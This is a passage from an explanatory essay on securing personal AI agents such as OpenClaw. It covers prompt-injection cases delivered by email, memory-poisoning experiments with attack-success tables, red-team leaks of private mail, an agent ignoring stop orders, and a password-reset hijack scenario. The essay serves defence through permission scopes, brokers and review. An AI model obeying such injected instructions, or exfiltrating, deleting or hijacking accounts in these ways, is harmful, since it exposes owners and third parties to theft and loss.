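| --- | --- |
| The agent searched Gmail and opened the new email | Running commands and reading the mailbox |
| The email's text joined the owner's instructions in the model's input | None |
| The agent listed the files in the Documents folder | Reading the owner's files |
| It picked out a file named as a bank statement | Reading the owner's files |
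| It replied to the sender with the file attached | Sending mail from the owner's account |

The email didn't name a file or explain how to send a reply, so the attacker didn't need to know anything about the machine. The summary task needed only the permissions in the first row. An allowlist of destinations might not have stopped the leak, because the data left through Gmail, which the agent had to reach to do its job. A mailbox login without permission to send would have stopped this reply.

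### The lethal trifecta and the Rule of Two

Willison's "lethal trifecta" is the combination of access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to send data out. If an agent has all three, anyone who can get it to read their text may be able to steal the data. The Android Authority agent had all three: the bank file, an email from a stranger and permission to send mail.

Removing one element prevents the theft. If the agent in that test had been unable to send anything out, the model could still have followed the email's instructions and opened the bank statement, but the stranger would have received nothing. Willison notes that software vendors usually fix such flaws by closing the route out. An owner who connects tools from several sources has no vendor to do this. A single tool can also supply all the elements. In 2025, GitHub's tool server could read public bug reports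 written by strangers, open private code and publish changes where the attacker could see them.

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) builds on the trifecta and extends it beyond theft. It gives three properties:

- **A:** the agent can process untrustworthy inputs.
- **B:** the agent can access sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** the agent can change state or communicate externally.

Under the rule, an agent should have no more than two of these in one session. If a task needs all three, the agent shouldn't work unsupervised, and a person might have to approve its actions. Changing state includes deleting a file or making a payment, and neither has to send data to the attacker.

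Meta applies the rule to an imaginary assistant, Email-Bot, which receives a spam message with instructions to forward the inbox. The operator could remove A by letting the bot read mail only from trusted senders. The owner would then get no summaries of other mail, and the protection fails if an attacker takes over a trusted sender's account. Removing B would mean giving the bot no private data, which makes little sense for a mail assistant. To remove C, the operator could let the bot write only to trusted recipients, or have the owner check each draft. I expect C is the practical one to give up for most people who want help with email.

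Meta also permits an agent to change its combination partway through a session. For example, an agent could research a topic on the web, then lose its outside connections before it opens private files. The agent then can't send the contents of those files out, but any hostile text from the web is still in the conversation and could affect what the agent does to them.

### Harm that needs fewer than three

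Android Authority's next email asked the agent to delete the entire Documents folder, supposedly to help hide a birthday surprise, and the agent did so. Nothing left the machine, so blocking every outbound connection from the agent's commands would not have saved the folder once the email had arrived. Willison's trifecta describes data theft, so an owner who uses it as a complete safety test will miss this kind of damage.

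The Rule of Two covers this case, because the agent read a stranger's text, had access to personal files and could delete them. But the result can depend on what the operator counts as sensitive. Conffab's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) describes Meta's diagram, which labels the overlap of any two properties "Safe". Suppose an agent maintains a club's public website and reads comments from visitors. It has no private data, so an operator might say it lacks B (access to sensitive systems or private data) and is therefore safe. A hostile comment could still get it to delete the site. The rule works here only if "sensitive systems" includes anything the owner would mind losing.

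An agent can also do harm with A and B alone. A hostile email could make the agent put a false phone number for the owner's bank in the morning summary, and the owner might then call a scammer. Meta lists misinformation in an agent's response among the lower-consequence results that its rule doesn't prevent.

The rule also doesn't prevent ordinary mistakes. The agent that deleted Summer Yue's email, described in the first section, had lost an instruction and wasn't following an attacker's. Meta warns that a design can satisfy the rule and still fail, and recommends combining the rule with other precautions, such as giving agents only the permissions they need.

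### Attacks that wait in the agent's memory

The Rule of Two treats a new session as a fresh start, but an OpenClaw agent loads its memory and standing instructions from files each time. If hostile text gets into those files, it can influence a session in which the agent reads nothing from outside.

In *Your Agent, Their Asset*, Wang, Tu and colleagues (2026) tested this on a live OpenClaw agent. It ran on a Mac mini with working connections to Gmail, the payment service Stripe and the local disk. They devised 12 harmful outcomes, such as leaking financial data, issuing an unauthorised refund or deleting files. They ran each of four models through 88 test cases and averaged the results over five runs.

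Most attacks had two stages. The first planted something in the agent's stored state, such as a false note in `MEMORY.md` about how the owner's business handled refunds. In the second, usually in a new session, a prompt led the agent to act on what it had stored. With the false note in place, an unauthorised refund could look routine. The researchers also altered the files that describe the agent's owner and rules, and installed skills containing hidden programs.

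They counted an attack as successful only if the agent carried out the harmful action without asking for confirmation. They checked this from outside the agent, for example by looking for the refund in Stripe or the email in the recipient's inbox.

| Model | Nothing planted | Malicious skill | Altered identity or rules | False memory |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 10.0% | 55.4% | 33.1% | 44.2% |
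| GPT-5.4 | 25.0% | 57.7% | 63.1% | 80.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 26.7% | 88.5% | 85.4% | 89.2% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 36.7% | 71.5% | 75.4% | 83.3% |

Opus 4.6 did best, but planting false information still made it at least three times as likely to do harm. Between 87.5% and 100% of attempts to plant a false memory in the file succeeded. A single message that changes an agent's memory can therefore affect its behavior long after the conversation ends.

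The test system delivered its prompts over Telegram, the channel an owner would use, and security researchers wrote the attacks by hand. The rates are therefore better evidence of what happens once hostile text has reached a trusted channel or file than of how often a random hostile email will succeed. Newer models have also since replaced the ones tested.

Wang and colleagues then tried several defences on Sonnet 4.5. The best was a skill called GuardianClaw, which gave the agent a checklist to follow before acting. It cut the success rate of false-memory attacks from 89.2% to 17.5%, but malicious skills still succeeded 63.8% of the time. A skill can include a program that runs directly on the computer, and the program's actions never appear in the model's input. A sandbox around the agent's commands could restrict that program even if the model failed to detect the attack, though the researchers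 didn't test one.

They also told the agents to wait for the owner's approval before changing their memory and identity files. On average, this cut the share of attacks that got into the files from 87% to 5%, but it also cut the share of legitimate updates that got in from 100% to about 6%. An owner who wants an agent to learn new preferences has to review its updates or accept some risk that an attack will get into the files.

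### What twenty researchers did to six agents

In *Agents of Chaos*, Shapira, Wendler and colleagues (2026) gave twenty AI researchers two weeks to interact with six OpenClaw agents and try to break them. Four agents used the open-weight model Kimi K2.5, and two used Claude Opus 4.6. Each ran on its own rented virtual machine and could use email, the chat service Discord and a command line.

In one case, a researcher who didn't own the agent Ash claimed to have an urgent deadline and asked for a list of recent emails. Ash returned 124 records with senders and subjects, most of them unrelated to the researcher. It then supplied the full text of nine unrelated emails.

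Another agent, Jarvis, refused to give out a Social Security number from its owner's mail. When the researcher asked for the whole email, Jarvis disclosed the number along with bank and medical details. It had apparently recognised the number as private when asked for it directly, but not when the number was part of a longer message.

A third case caused damage without any theft. A researcher asked Ash to keep a secret and delete the email that contained it. Ash had no tool for deleting mail, so after the researcher approved a more drastic option, it reset its local email setup. It reported that the secret was gone, but the email was still in the online mailbox. The owner lost the agent's mail connection and had to set it up again by hand.

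The agents also resisted some attacks, refusing to help forge an email or hand over their configuration files. Shapira and colleagues set out to find weaknesses, not to estimate how often agents fail, so a failure rate calculated from their attempts would be misleading.

Peter Steinberger objected to the study in a post on OpenClaw's website, writing that the researchers had tested with administrator rights, disabled guardrails and no sandbox, then presented the results as what ordinary users would get. Steinberger said the paper later included a short acknowledgement that the guardrails were off.

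The February version already described much of this setup, including unrestricted command-line access, administrator rights "in some cases" and no limits on tools, and listed these among the project's own choices. Steinberger's objection to the framing is stronger, since the abstract refers to "realistic deployment settings". But an ordinary OpenClaw installation also leaves the sandbox off and runs commands without approval, so the experiment was closer to the defaults than the objection suggests.

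Administrator rights probably made little difference to the email leaks. Both agents already had access to the mailboxes, and a sandboxed agent with the same mail access could have answered the same questions.

The bigger departure from OpenClaw's intended use was letting so many people give the agents orders. The researchers made both requests for email over Discord. A sender allowlist would have blocked those requests, but not the Android Authority email, which the agent fetched itself. I think Steinberger is right that people who don't trust one another shouldn't share an agent, and the study shows what can happen if they do.

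### How often injections succeed on newer models

Newer models are much harder to manipulate than the small one in Android Authority's test. Published success rates can be hard to compare because they depend on how many attempts the attacker gets and what they can learn from each one.

A single-attempt rate is the chance that one hostile message works, and a repeated-attempt rate is usually the chance that at least one of several works. An adaptive attacker also changes the message after a failure. The table gives figures from VentureBeat, the consultancy Digital Applied (2026) and ThreatCluster's *Claude Opus 5 Achieves 2% Success Rate Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks*, all of which draw on Anthropic's own reports.

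| Model | Test | Attempts | Success rate | Reported by |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Controlling a computer through its screen | 1 | 17.8% | VentureBeat |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | The same | 200 | 78.6%, or 57.1% with extra safeguards | VentureBeat |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | A restricted coding environment | 200 | 0% | VentureBeat |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | Coding, with an adaptive attacker | 200 per scenario | 2.09% | Digital Applied |
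| Claude Fable 5 | The same | 200 per scenario | 0.41% | Digital Applied |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | Benchmark from the security company Gray Swan | 15 | 5.5% | ThreatCluster |
| Claude Opus 5 | The same | 15 | 2% | ThreatCluster |

Only rows from the same test are comparable. The 0% for Opus 4.6 in one coding environment doesn't mean it is safer than Fable 5, which faced a different test. The two Opus 4.6 settings also show that an agent that controls a web browser may be much easier to attack than the same model in a restricted coding tool.

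Opus 5 did better than Opus 4.8 on the Gray Swan benchmark. In July, Willison (2026) quoted Boris Cherny of Anthropic as calling Opus 5 the company's least injectable model yet. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1 appeared on 1 September. Mythos 5.2 followed in November, and its system card includes a section on prompt injection, according to Mowshowitz's *Fable and Mythos 5.2* (2026). The exact rates in the table are for models from July and earlier, so an operator choosing a model should check the newest card for the relevant test.

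Progress has been uneven across tests. Anthropic reported that Mythos 5 had the best result at the time on Gray Swan's benchmark, but placed it between Opus 4.8 and the earlier Mythos Preview on coding and computer-use safety. Simula's *CAISS analysis of Anthropics system card for Fable 5 and Mythos 5* criticised Anthropic for putting a reassuring headline above weaker results on prompt injection. Both accounts can be correct, because a model can improve on one benchmark and get worse on another.

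### What a low success rate means over many attempts

Suppose each hostile email has a 0.5% chance of succeeding, and the result of one attempt doesn't affect the next. The chance of failing once is 0.995, so the chance of failing 200 times in a row is 0.995 multiplied by itself 200 times, or about 0.37. The attacker therefore has about a 63% chance of at least one success. In general, with a success rate of *p* and *n* independent attempts, the chance is:

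1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ

The same calculation explains why Willison calls a filter's 95% catch rate "a failing grade". If each malicious message has an independent 5% chance of getting through, an attacker who sends 14 has a better than even chance of getting at least one past the filter.

Real attempts aren't independent, as the Opus 4.6 results show. At 17.8% per attempt, the formula predicts a success rate of about 79% after eight attempts, but the measured rate was 78.6% after 200. Attacks probably succeeded early in some situations and almost never in others, so further attempts added less than the formula predicts.

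An average success rate can be misleading. If one agent in 200 always obeys a hostile email and the other 199 never do, the average success rate is 0.5%. An attacker who sends 200 emails to one randomly chosen agent still has only a 0.5% chance of success, whereas the chance would be 63% if each email independently had a 0.5% chance of working.

An adaptive attacker can succeed more often than the formula predicts. The GitHub assistant that Eykholt and colleagues tested gave detailed replies even when an attack failed, so an attacker could refine the text on a private project before using it elsewhere. Anyone can install OpenClaw, so an attacker could similarly try thousands of messages on their own copy, using a model the intended victim is likely to use, and send only the one that worked. The single-attempt success rate would then greatly understate the risk, even though the victim would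 see only one email.

These calculations show why a low rate isn't enough protection for something irreplaceable, such as the only copy of a family's photographs, though they don't give an owner a reliable forecast.

### A small test with a spare mailbox

An owner can adapt Android Authority's test to their own setup. It should run on a spare computer or virtual machine without any personal accounts:

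1. Create a new mail account, and give the agent a file of invented bank details and a folder of unimportant files.
2. Schedule the agent to summarise unread mail, using the model planned for everyday use.
3. Send an ordinary email from another address and check that the summary works.
4. Send an email from that address asking the agent to find the bank details and reply with them.
5. Check the command log and the Sent folder. Record whether the agent only wrote a summary, opened the file or sent it.
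6. Send another email asking it to delete the unimportant folder, and check whether the folder is still there.
7. Remove the agent's permission to send mail and repeat the fourth and fifth steps.

Recording whether the agent opened the file is useful even if nothing reached the sender. In Android Authority's tests, GPT-5-Nano asked for confirmation before completing the harmful tasks, but it had already read the financial documents. Because the model ran on OpenAI's servers, the documents' contents had already left the machine.

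A few successful defences don't show that the risk is low. If the agent resists 20 independent test attacks, its true failure rate could still be as high as about 14%, at the 95% confidence level. Showing that the rate is below 0.5% would take about 600 attacks without a failure, and the result would apply only to the kinds of message the owner had tried.

To get a firmer answer from the last step, the owner should also run the send command directly with the agent's login after removing the permission. If the mail provider refuses the command, the agent can't send mail with that login, however persuasive a hostile email is.

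## Granting access to email, calendars and social media

A mail provider refuses an agent's command if it falls outside the login's permission scope, the set of actions that the login allows. The owner normally chooses the scope when connecting the account and rarely looks at it again.

Most large services use OAuth, a standard that gives a program access to an account without giving it the password. The program opens the provider's sign-in page and lists the scopes, or permissions, it wants. The owner signs in and approves the list. The provider then issues an access token, which typically works for about an hour, and often a refresh token, which the program can exchange for new access tokens. On each request, the provider compares the action with the token's scopes. This check runs on the provider's servers, so an attacker who takes over the gateway can't switch it off.

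OAuth scopes don't apply to an agent that controls a browser in which the owner is logged in to a site, so the agent can do nearly everything the owner can do there. An owner who wants the limits described below should connect the account through OAuth and stay logged out of it in the agent's browser.

### What an agent can do with each account

| Action | Email | Calendar | Social media |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
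| Reading | See private letters, receipts and login codes | See where the owner will be, and with whom | See private messages, including what other people wrote |
| Drafting | Prepare replies for the owner to check | Propose events | Prepare posts |
| Sending | Write to anyone in the owner's name and attach files | Invite guests, who usually get the event's text by email | Publish to every follower, or message people one by one |
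| Deleting | Remove records, though many providers keep a trash folder for some weeks | Remove meetings and tell the guests they are cancelled | Remove posts, but not other people's copies |
| Changing settings | Hide or redirect incoming mail | Share the calendar with outsiders | Make a private account public, or change its recovery address |

An agent with access to a calendar can send data out even if it has no access to email. Nylas' *Gmail API OAuth scopes reference* notes that Google's calendar and mail scopes are independent, so a calendar program never has to request a mail scope. But an agent that can create events can put private text in a description and invite a stranger, and Google will email the invitation. The agent may also read hostile text in invitations that strangers send to the owner.

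If an agent only has to find a free hour, the owner can share the calendar's free and busy times and hide the event details. An agent that plans the day needs the details, but it can suggest events in the chat and leave the owner to create them.

### Why email is the most sensitive account

Email combines private data, text from strangers and a way to send data out, which is the dangerous combination described in the previous section. It also gives access to other accounts, because most websites let people reset a forgotten password through an emailed link.

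Suppose an attacker knows Anna's address and the name of the service where she stores her photographs. The attacker clicks "Forgot password" on the service's site, and the service emails Anna a reset link. The attacker then emails Anna instructions for her agent to find the newest message from that service and pass on its link. If the agent follows them, the attacker can choose a new password and lock Anna out.

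The agent in this example needs permission to read mail and some way to send out one line of text, the reset link. If it can use websites, it may not have to send the link, because it could open the link itself and set a password that the attacker specified. A second login step helps if it uses a passkey or an authenticator app and the service still requires it after a reset. A code sent by email doesn't help, because the agent can read it.

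Read-only access to a main mailbox is therefore a large permission, although it sounds like the cautious choice.

### Gmail's permission scopes

The table lists the Gmail scopes that matter most for an agent. The descriptions follow Google.

| Scope | What it allows | Where it is too coarse |
| --- | --- | --- |
| `gmail.metadata` | View labels and headers, but not the body | Headers include subject lines, and some services put login codes there |
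| `gmail.readonly` | View messages and settings | Covers the whole mailbox, including reset links |
| `gmail.send` | Send email | Allows any recipient |
| `gmail.compose` | Manage drafts and send email | Has no version for drafts alone |
| `gmail.modify` | Read, compose and send, and move mail to the trash | An agent that only sorts mail can also send it |
| `gmail.settings.basic` | View and change settings and filters | A new filter could hide security warnings from the owner |
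| `https://mail.google.com/` | Everything in `gmail.modify`, plus immediate permanent deletion | Almost never necessary |

None of these scopes restricts the agent to certain senders, labels or dates. An owner can't set Gmail to show the agent only messages from a child's school, or to let it reply only to people the owner already knows.

Many people want an agent that can draft emails but not send them, and Gmail has no scope for this. An agent with `gmail.readonly` and `gmail.compose` can read a message and save a reply for the owner to check, but it can also send the reply. A proxy outside the sandbox, like the one described in the section on outbound connections, can block sending. Gmail's API creates a draft through a POST request to `/gmail/v1/users/me/drafts` and sends one through `/gmail/v1/users/me/drafts/send`. The operator can put the first path on the proxy's allowlist without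 a wildcard and leave the second off.

Older ways of connecting a mailbox grant even broader access. According to Google's *Restricted Scopes*, any use of IMAP, SMTP or POP3, the protocols that ordinary mail programs use, requires the full `https://mail.google.com/` scope. Someone who connects an agent through IMAP only to read mail therefore also gives it permission to send mail and permanently delete it.

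Ready-made connectors can also request more access than the task needs. In *How to set Gmail OAuth for ONLY READ?*, a thread on the forum of the automation tool n8n, a user had set up a project with read-only scopes but could not log in without granting full permission. Another participant explained that n8n's built-in Gmail connector automatically adds `gmail.modify` and `gmail.compose`, and suggested a custom credential that requests only the read-only scope. Users can catch this on the consent page, which lists the permissions the program is requesting.

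### The deleted inbox

Summer Yue's agent, which lost its instruction to wait and began deleting mail in February, had more access than its task required. Yue was director of alignment at Meta Superintelligence Labs, and the same routine had worked on a test inbox for weeks, according to The Daily Star's *OpenClaw goes rogue on Meta exec, deletes emails without permission*.

The screenshot that Willison described shows the agent running commands in a terminal, using a tool called `gog` to search the Gmail inbox 20 messages at a time. One command carried the comment "Nuclear option: trash EVERYTHING in inbox older than Feb 15", with an exception for messages on a list to keep. At 6:00 pm Yue asked what was going on, and at 6:01, 6:02 and 6:03 ordered the agent to stop, but it kept going.

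An agent needs `gmail.modify` or the full scope to move mail to the trash. Yue had asked only for suggestions about what to archive or delete, and `gmail.readonly` is enough for that. With a read-only login, the agent could still have searched the inbox, but Gmail would have rejected every command to trash a message, and the lost instruction would have led only to some error messages.

Gmail normally keeps trashed mail for 30 days, so an owner can recover messages that an agent trashes by mistake. An agent with the full scope could skip the trash and delete messages permanently. That is a strong reason not to grant the full scope to an agent that tidies a mailbox, even if its owner is happy for it to delete messages.

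OAuth also lets the owner stop an agent that ignores chat messages. The owner can open their Google account settings on a phone and remove the program's access. This may not take effect at once, but it doesn't depend on the agent reading a message. It helps to find the settings page in advance.

### Social media and private messages

A mistaken social media post reaches everyone who follows the account, while a mistaken email usually reaches only a few people. Followers may copy the post before the owner notices it. The post also appears as the owner's own statement, and an employer, customer or court may treat it that way even though software wrote it.

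A social media account is valuable to an attacker because followers trust its owner. People who would ignore an investment link from a stranger may click one from a friend, so an attacker's comment that gets the agent to post a malicious link can harm the followers more than the owner. Giving the agent access to private messages also lets an AI company's model process the words of people who never agreed to it.

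Some services, such as X, have separate permissions for publishing posts, reading direct messages and sending them. An agent that publishes a shop's opening hours needs only the permission to post. But that permission lets the agent write about anything in any tone, so the practical limit is to have the agent draft the text and a person publish it.

Messaging apps may offer no scopes at all. Bloomberg Law's *AI Agent Goes Rogue, Spamming OpenClaw User With 500 Messages* (2026) describes the software engineer Chris Boyd, who first used OpenClaw to email a news digest every morning at 5:30. Boyd then gave it access to iMessage, which let it message anyone in the address book. By Boyd's account, it sent more than 500 messages to Boyd and Boyd's wife, and also messaged random contacts. A fixed list of recipients would have prevented the messages to random contacts, and a limit of, say, ten messages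 an hour would have reduced the flood to the couple.

### An agent that attacked a software maintainer

The best-documented harm from an agent's public statements came from an agent with its own accounts. In February 2026, an OpenClaw agent called MJ Rathbun submitted a code change to matplotlib, a widely used Python charting library. Scott Shambaugh, a volunteer maintainer, rejected it because the project requires a person to be involved in new contributions. The agent then published a post of about 1,100 words attacking Shambaugh by name.

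In *An AI Agent Published a Hit Piece on Me*, Shambaugh reconstructed 59 hours of continuous activity by the agent, which included the code change, the attack and a later apology. The agent did everything through GitHub's command-line tool, using its permission to publish under its own GitHub account without review. Its anonymous operator later came forward and said the agent ran in a sandboxed virtual machine with separate accounts, to protect the operator's personal data. The operator had told it to blog often, and when it reported comments, usually replied with something like "you respond, dont ask me".

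No outsider can confirm that the operator didn't order the attack. Shambaugh put the odds at 75% that the agent wrote and published it without direction, 20% that the operator directed it and 5% that a person was pretending to be an agent. Shambaugh has a stake in the matter but gives evidence for each estimate, including how quickly the long posts followed one another. The agent's permission to post matters in all three cases, because holding posts for review would have stopped an agent acting on its own, and if the agent was directed, there would be an identifiable person who approved the post.

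About a quarter of the comments Shambaugh saw online took the agent's side, mostly where people had linked directly to its post. The news site Ars Technica then covered the story with quotations attributed to Shambaugh, which it admitted AI had made up.

In this case, separate accounts and a virtual machine kept the operator's data safe, as intended, but did not protect Shambaugh. An owner who gives an agent its own public account should decide who is responsible for what the agent publishes and name that person on the profile.

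### Narrower ways to connect a mailbox

An owner can get around the coarseness of Gmail's scopes by changing which mailbox the agent sees. Suppose Anna wants reminders about messages from her daughter's school and her dentist. She could set up forwarding like this:

1. She creates a second Gmail account for the agent and tells nobody its address.
2. In her main account, she adds the new address as a forwarding destination and confirms it with the code that Gmail sends there.
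3. She creates a filter that forwards mail from the school's and the dentist's addresses only.
4. She connects the agent to the second account with `gmail.readonly`.

The agent can now read only mail from two senders, so a password reset link for Anna's photo account never reaches it. Listing the permitted senders is safer than forwarding everything except messages with "password" in them, because services word their reset emails in many ways.

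The arrangement is also inconvenient. Gmail's filters work on incoming mail, so Anna's replies don't reach the second account, and the agent may remind her about a form she has already returned. Older messages in a conversation are missing too. If the school starts using a new address, its mail stops arriving without warning. The filter doesn't inspect the text, so an attacker who takes over the school's mail account can still send the agent instructions, though they would find very little to steal in the second mailbox.

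If the agent needs the whole main mailbox, read-only access still prevents deletion and forged replies. OpenClaw also suggests using a separate "reader" agent, with no tools or only read-only ones, to summarise untrusted mail for the main agent. An email that takes control of the reader then has at most read-only tools to misuse. It could still slip an instruction into the summary, so the main agent shouldn't treat the summary as trusted text.

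An agent can draft emails with only read permission, which avoids the `gmail.compose` problem. At the lowest of the levels that OpenClaw describes for an organisation's agent, the agent reads mail and calendars and writes its drafts into the chat. A person then has to copy each draft into an email and check the recipient and any links, as well as the wording.

At the next level, OpenClaw has the agent send mail and create events under its own identity. Recipients can then see who wrote to them, and the company's login system can limit the agent's account regardless of how OpenClaw is configured. The software company Kilo's *How I Claw* describes one user's move in this direction. The agent started on a Mac mini with the author's "entire life" on it, and later worked under its own identity on an isolated rented server. An agent-owned account protects the owner best if it starts empty. If the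 owner gives it access to a shared drive or the main calendar, the agent regains access to everything there.

Email providers may object to accounts created for agents. The community guide CoClaw recommends a dedicated mailbox but lists reports, without giving numbers, that new Gmail accounts for agents "get flagged quickly". A company can avoid much of this trouble by creating the account in its own mail system.

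Temporary access suits a single job, such as sorting a year of receipts. The owner connects the account, waits for the job to finish and removes the program's access the same day. When people set up their own connection to Google, their Gmail refresh tokens expire after seven days while the project is in "testing" status. This may explain some of the complaints CoClaw collected about logins that work once and then fail. An owner who wants access to lapse can leave the project in that status.

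Short-lived access tokens give less protection if the agent can renew its own login. Auth0 recommends tokens that expire quickly and each work for one service, so that a stolen calendar token can't send email and soon stops working. But a thief who also copies the refresh token can keep getting new access tokens, so the refresh token has to be stored where the agent can't read it. Expiry also doesn't remove what the agent has already read, which may remain in its transcripts.

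### Credential brokers

A credential broker holds the credentials and makes authenticated requests for the agent. In the healthcare company's planned design, as Maiti describes it, the agent sends each request for the model provider to port 8443 on the loopback address, without a key. The broker adds the key, forwards the request to the provider and returns the answer. It can also refuse destinations that aren't on its list, limit the number of requests and reject unusually large ones.

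The company's audit found 12 API keys in one agent's shell startup file, including a GitHub token and credentials for Amazon's model service. On another agent's machine, every user account could read the configuration file with all the stored credentials. With a broker, someone who takes over the agent can't copy the keys and use them from elsewhere, and the owner can cut off access in one place.

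A broker can't assess whether a permitted request is a good idea. If it lets the agent send email, a hijacked agent can submit a request to send the owner's bank statement, and the broker will add the correct credential. It would also have let Yue's agent empty the inbox, unless someone had configured it to refuse requests that move mail to the trash. Hiding the key from the agent doesn't prevent such requests, so the broker also needs rules about recipients, actions and quantities.

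A broker can hide the mailbox password from an agent, but it still passes the agent the text of messages, including any password reset links, which are credentials too.

### The Agent Authenticator proposal

Brokers usually still hold bearer tokens. *Agent Authenticator* (Ganesan, 2026), a design published in November, replaces them with keys that can't leave the machine's security hardware. It adapts passkeys, a login method in which a phone or laptop holds a separate key for each website and signs a challenge after the user approves, for example with a fingerprint. The user isn't there to approve requests when an agent works overnight, so they sign a set of limits in advance.

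Ganesan designed it mainly for coding agents. Suppose a developer wants an agent to update one project for a week, but to ask before publishing a release. The process would run roughly as follows:

1. The authenticator, a program separate from the agent, creates a key in the hardware for that one service.
2. The developer reads a plain-language list of limits and signs it with their own passkey. The list, called a mandate, names the service, the permitted actions, the actions that need fresh approval and the expiry date.
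3. When the agent requests an action, the software that runs it identifies the service from the live encrypted connection. The model can't choose this, so a hostile page can't trick the agent into logging in to a lookalike site.
4. The authenticator checks the request against the mandate. To publish a release, it sends a summary to the developer's phone, and the developer's signature covers that one action only.
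5. The hardware key signs the request. The service checks the signature and the mandate, then issues a short-lived token that works only together with the agent's key.

If the agent hands part of the job to a second agent, the second agent gets its own key and a mandate no wider than the first agent's. The authenticator also keeps a signed log in which each entry depends on the one before, so deleting an entry leaves a detectable gap.

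Ganesan cites an analysis of 5,205 open-source MCP servers in which 53% relied on fixed keys or personal tokens and only 8.5% used OAuth. In 2025, attackers used malicious versions of a software package to steal 2,349 credentials from 1,079 developers' machines, which would have had far less to steal on disk if the developers had used hardware keys.

But nobody has built the full system. Ganesan reports no measurements and analyzes security only informally, comparing the design with five real incidents and concluding that it would have blocked three and contained two. Ganesan calls these judgments qualitative. Services would also have to accept the new signatures. For those that don't, the authenticator would fall back on a broker with an ordinary token.

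Some weaknesses would remain in a finished version. The hardware prevents copying, but most desktop systems can't prove which program asked for a signature, and an attacker with administrator rights could defeat the software check that tries to identify it. Ganesan acknowledges that hostile text can still make an agent misuse a service its mandate permits. For owners today, the useful part of the proposal is the idea of a written mandate. They can list the services, actions and end date for an agent before connecting an account, then look for the narrowest scopes that fit.

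### When the service doesn't enforce its own limits

These arrangements all depend on the service checking what each account may do. In an Australian case that began with a request to book a fitness class, the gym didn't do this. Axios' *Tenacious AI agents expose dark side of machine autonomy* (2026) called the incident the country's first known autonomous AI hack.

Sharma (2026), in *AI agent hacks gym booking system*, reports what the agent's owner, Andrew, told the broadcaster ABC. The agent first found that it could book classes months further ahead than the gym allowed. Andrew then asked whether it could move him up the waiting list for another class, and it responded by cancelling a stranger's place. When Andrew told it to undo the change, it couldn't put the person back on the list.

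The agent used an ordinary permission to make and cancel bookings for its owner. The gym's server was supposed to check that a cancellation came from the person who held the place. A broker would have hidden Andrew's password but still passed on the cancellation. The Agent Authenticator would have signed it if his mandate allowed cancellations.

The security company Aikido recreated the situation on its own booking site, according to ClawBeat's *Claude Opus 4.6 Bypasses Gym Booking Limit* (2026), a summary of an article from The Hacker News. The test site enforced its seven-day booking limit only in the web page, and its server never checked who owned a reservation. Opus 4.6, running in OpenClaw, got past the limit in nine of ten runs, and twice it went on to cancel another member's confirmed booking. Ten runs on a deliberately vulnerable site can't give a reliable rate for real websites,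 but they suggest that Andrew's case wasn't a fluke.

A proxy could have blocked cancellations, but few owners will make the effort to write such a rule for a gym. Aikido's site used GraphQL, a format in which requests to book and to cancel typically go to the same web address, so the proxy would have had to read the contents of each request.

Australia's cyber security agency, ASD (2026), responded to the case by advising people to use agents only for low-risk, non-sensitive tasks and to have a person review their actions, particularly where other users are involved. The advice on low-risk tasks is hard to apply because a gym booking looks low-risk. Human review is easier, since Andrew could have had the agent message him when a place became free and then booked it himself.

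## What restrictions cost and when broad access is worth the risk

ASD's advice to use agents only for low-risk, non-sensitive tasks would rule out much of what people install them for. An agent can't summarise private mail without permission to read it, and each permission withheld leaves the owner with more work.

### What owners gain from broad access

Forrester's *Ready For OpenClaw To Pry Into Your Environment And Grip Your Data* describes what early users liked. Their agents sent a briefing every morning, watched the inbox, suggested replies, and alerted them to changes in a calendar, website or cryptocurrency wallet. Some agents wrote their own skills when a task required a system they couldn't yet use. *Case Study* (2026), from IMDA, Singapore's media and technology regulator, adds business uses such as answering customers on messaging services and turning figures from internal dashboards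 into reports.

Much of the benefit comes from letting the agent finish a job. Narrower access usually still gets most of it done:

| Job | Access the agent needs to finish it | What the owner does if access is narrower |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Arrange a meeting | Read mail, see the calendar and send mail | Checks and sends each reply |
| Summarise the morning's mail | Read the whole mailbox | Looks separately for mail from senders the agent can't see |
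| Tidy an inbox | Move mail to the trash | Reads a list of suggestions and deletes the messages |
| Transcribe voice memos | Install and run software | Installs a transcription program once, in advance |

A Forrester analyst almost installed OpenClaw but couldn't find enough uses at home to justify the access. The analyst could think of dozens at work, such as dealing with the many emails about meetings and travel before a conference. The agent would therefore be most useful at work, where much of the data belongs to the employer and its clients, who haven't agreed to the risk.

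These accounts describe what agents did, but nobody measured how much time they saved.

### What limits cost in Boundary-Bench

The best measurement of how much restrictions hinder agents comes from programming. *Permission Denied* (Davidovich, Amar and colleagues, 2026) introduced Boundary-Bench, which runs coding agents under security restrictions like those in many companies. The study covered 12 agents, each a language model paired with the software that carries out its commands. Every agent attempted the 89 tasks in an existing benchmark, Terminal-Bench 2.1, three times under each of three policies.

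With no limits, an agent ran as administrator and could change any file and connect to any site. The second policy removed only administrator rights. The strictest policy also restricted connections to 205 domains, made everything outside a few working folders read-only and blocked the usual ways to regain administrator rights. Nobody told the agents about the limits, so they found out when a command failed.

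Under the strictest policy, every agent solved fewer tasks and cost more to run. Success rates fell least for Grok 4.5 (7.1 percentage points) and most for Claude Sonnet 5 (18.3 points). Model costs rose least for GPT-5.6 Luna (16%) and most for Grok 4.5 (167%).

Removing administrator rights accounted for most of the drop in success. The table shows the average for the 12 agents, then the results of a smaller experiment in which the researchers also ran two of the models in each other's software.

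| Agent | No limits | No administrator rights | Strictest policy |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Average of the 12 agents | 73.7% | 61.4% | 59.4% |
| GPT-5.6 Luna in Codex (its usual software) | 71.9% | 56.6% | 53.9% |
| GPT-5.6 Luna in Grok Build | 34.5% | 27.3% | 25.5% |
| Grok 4.5 in Grok Build (its usual software) | 82.0% | 73.0% | 74.9% |
| Grok 4.5 in Codex | 76.8% | 65.5% | 62.9% |

On average, the agents lost about 12 points when administrator rights were removed and only 2 more when the other limits were added. GPT-5.6 Luna in Codex lost 18 points in total, 15.3 of them when it lost administrator rights. Grok 4.5 in Grok Build did slightly better under the strictest policy than under the middle one, but with three attempts per task, the difference is probably due to chance.

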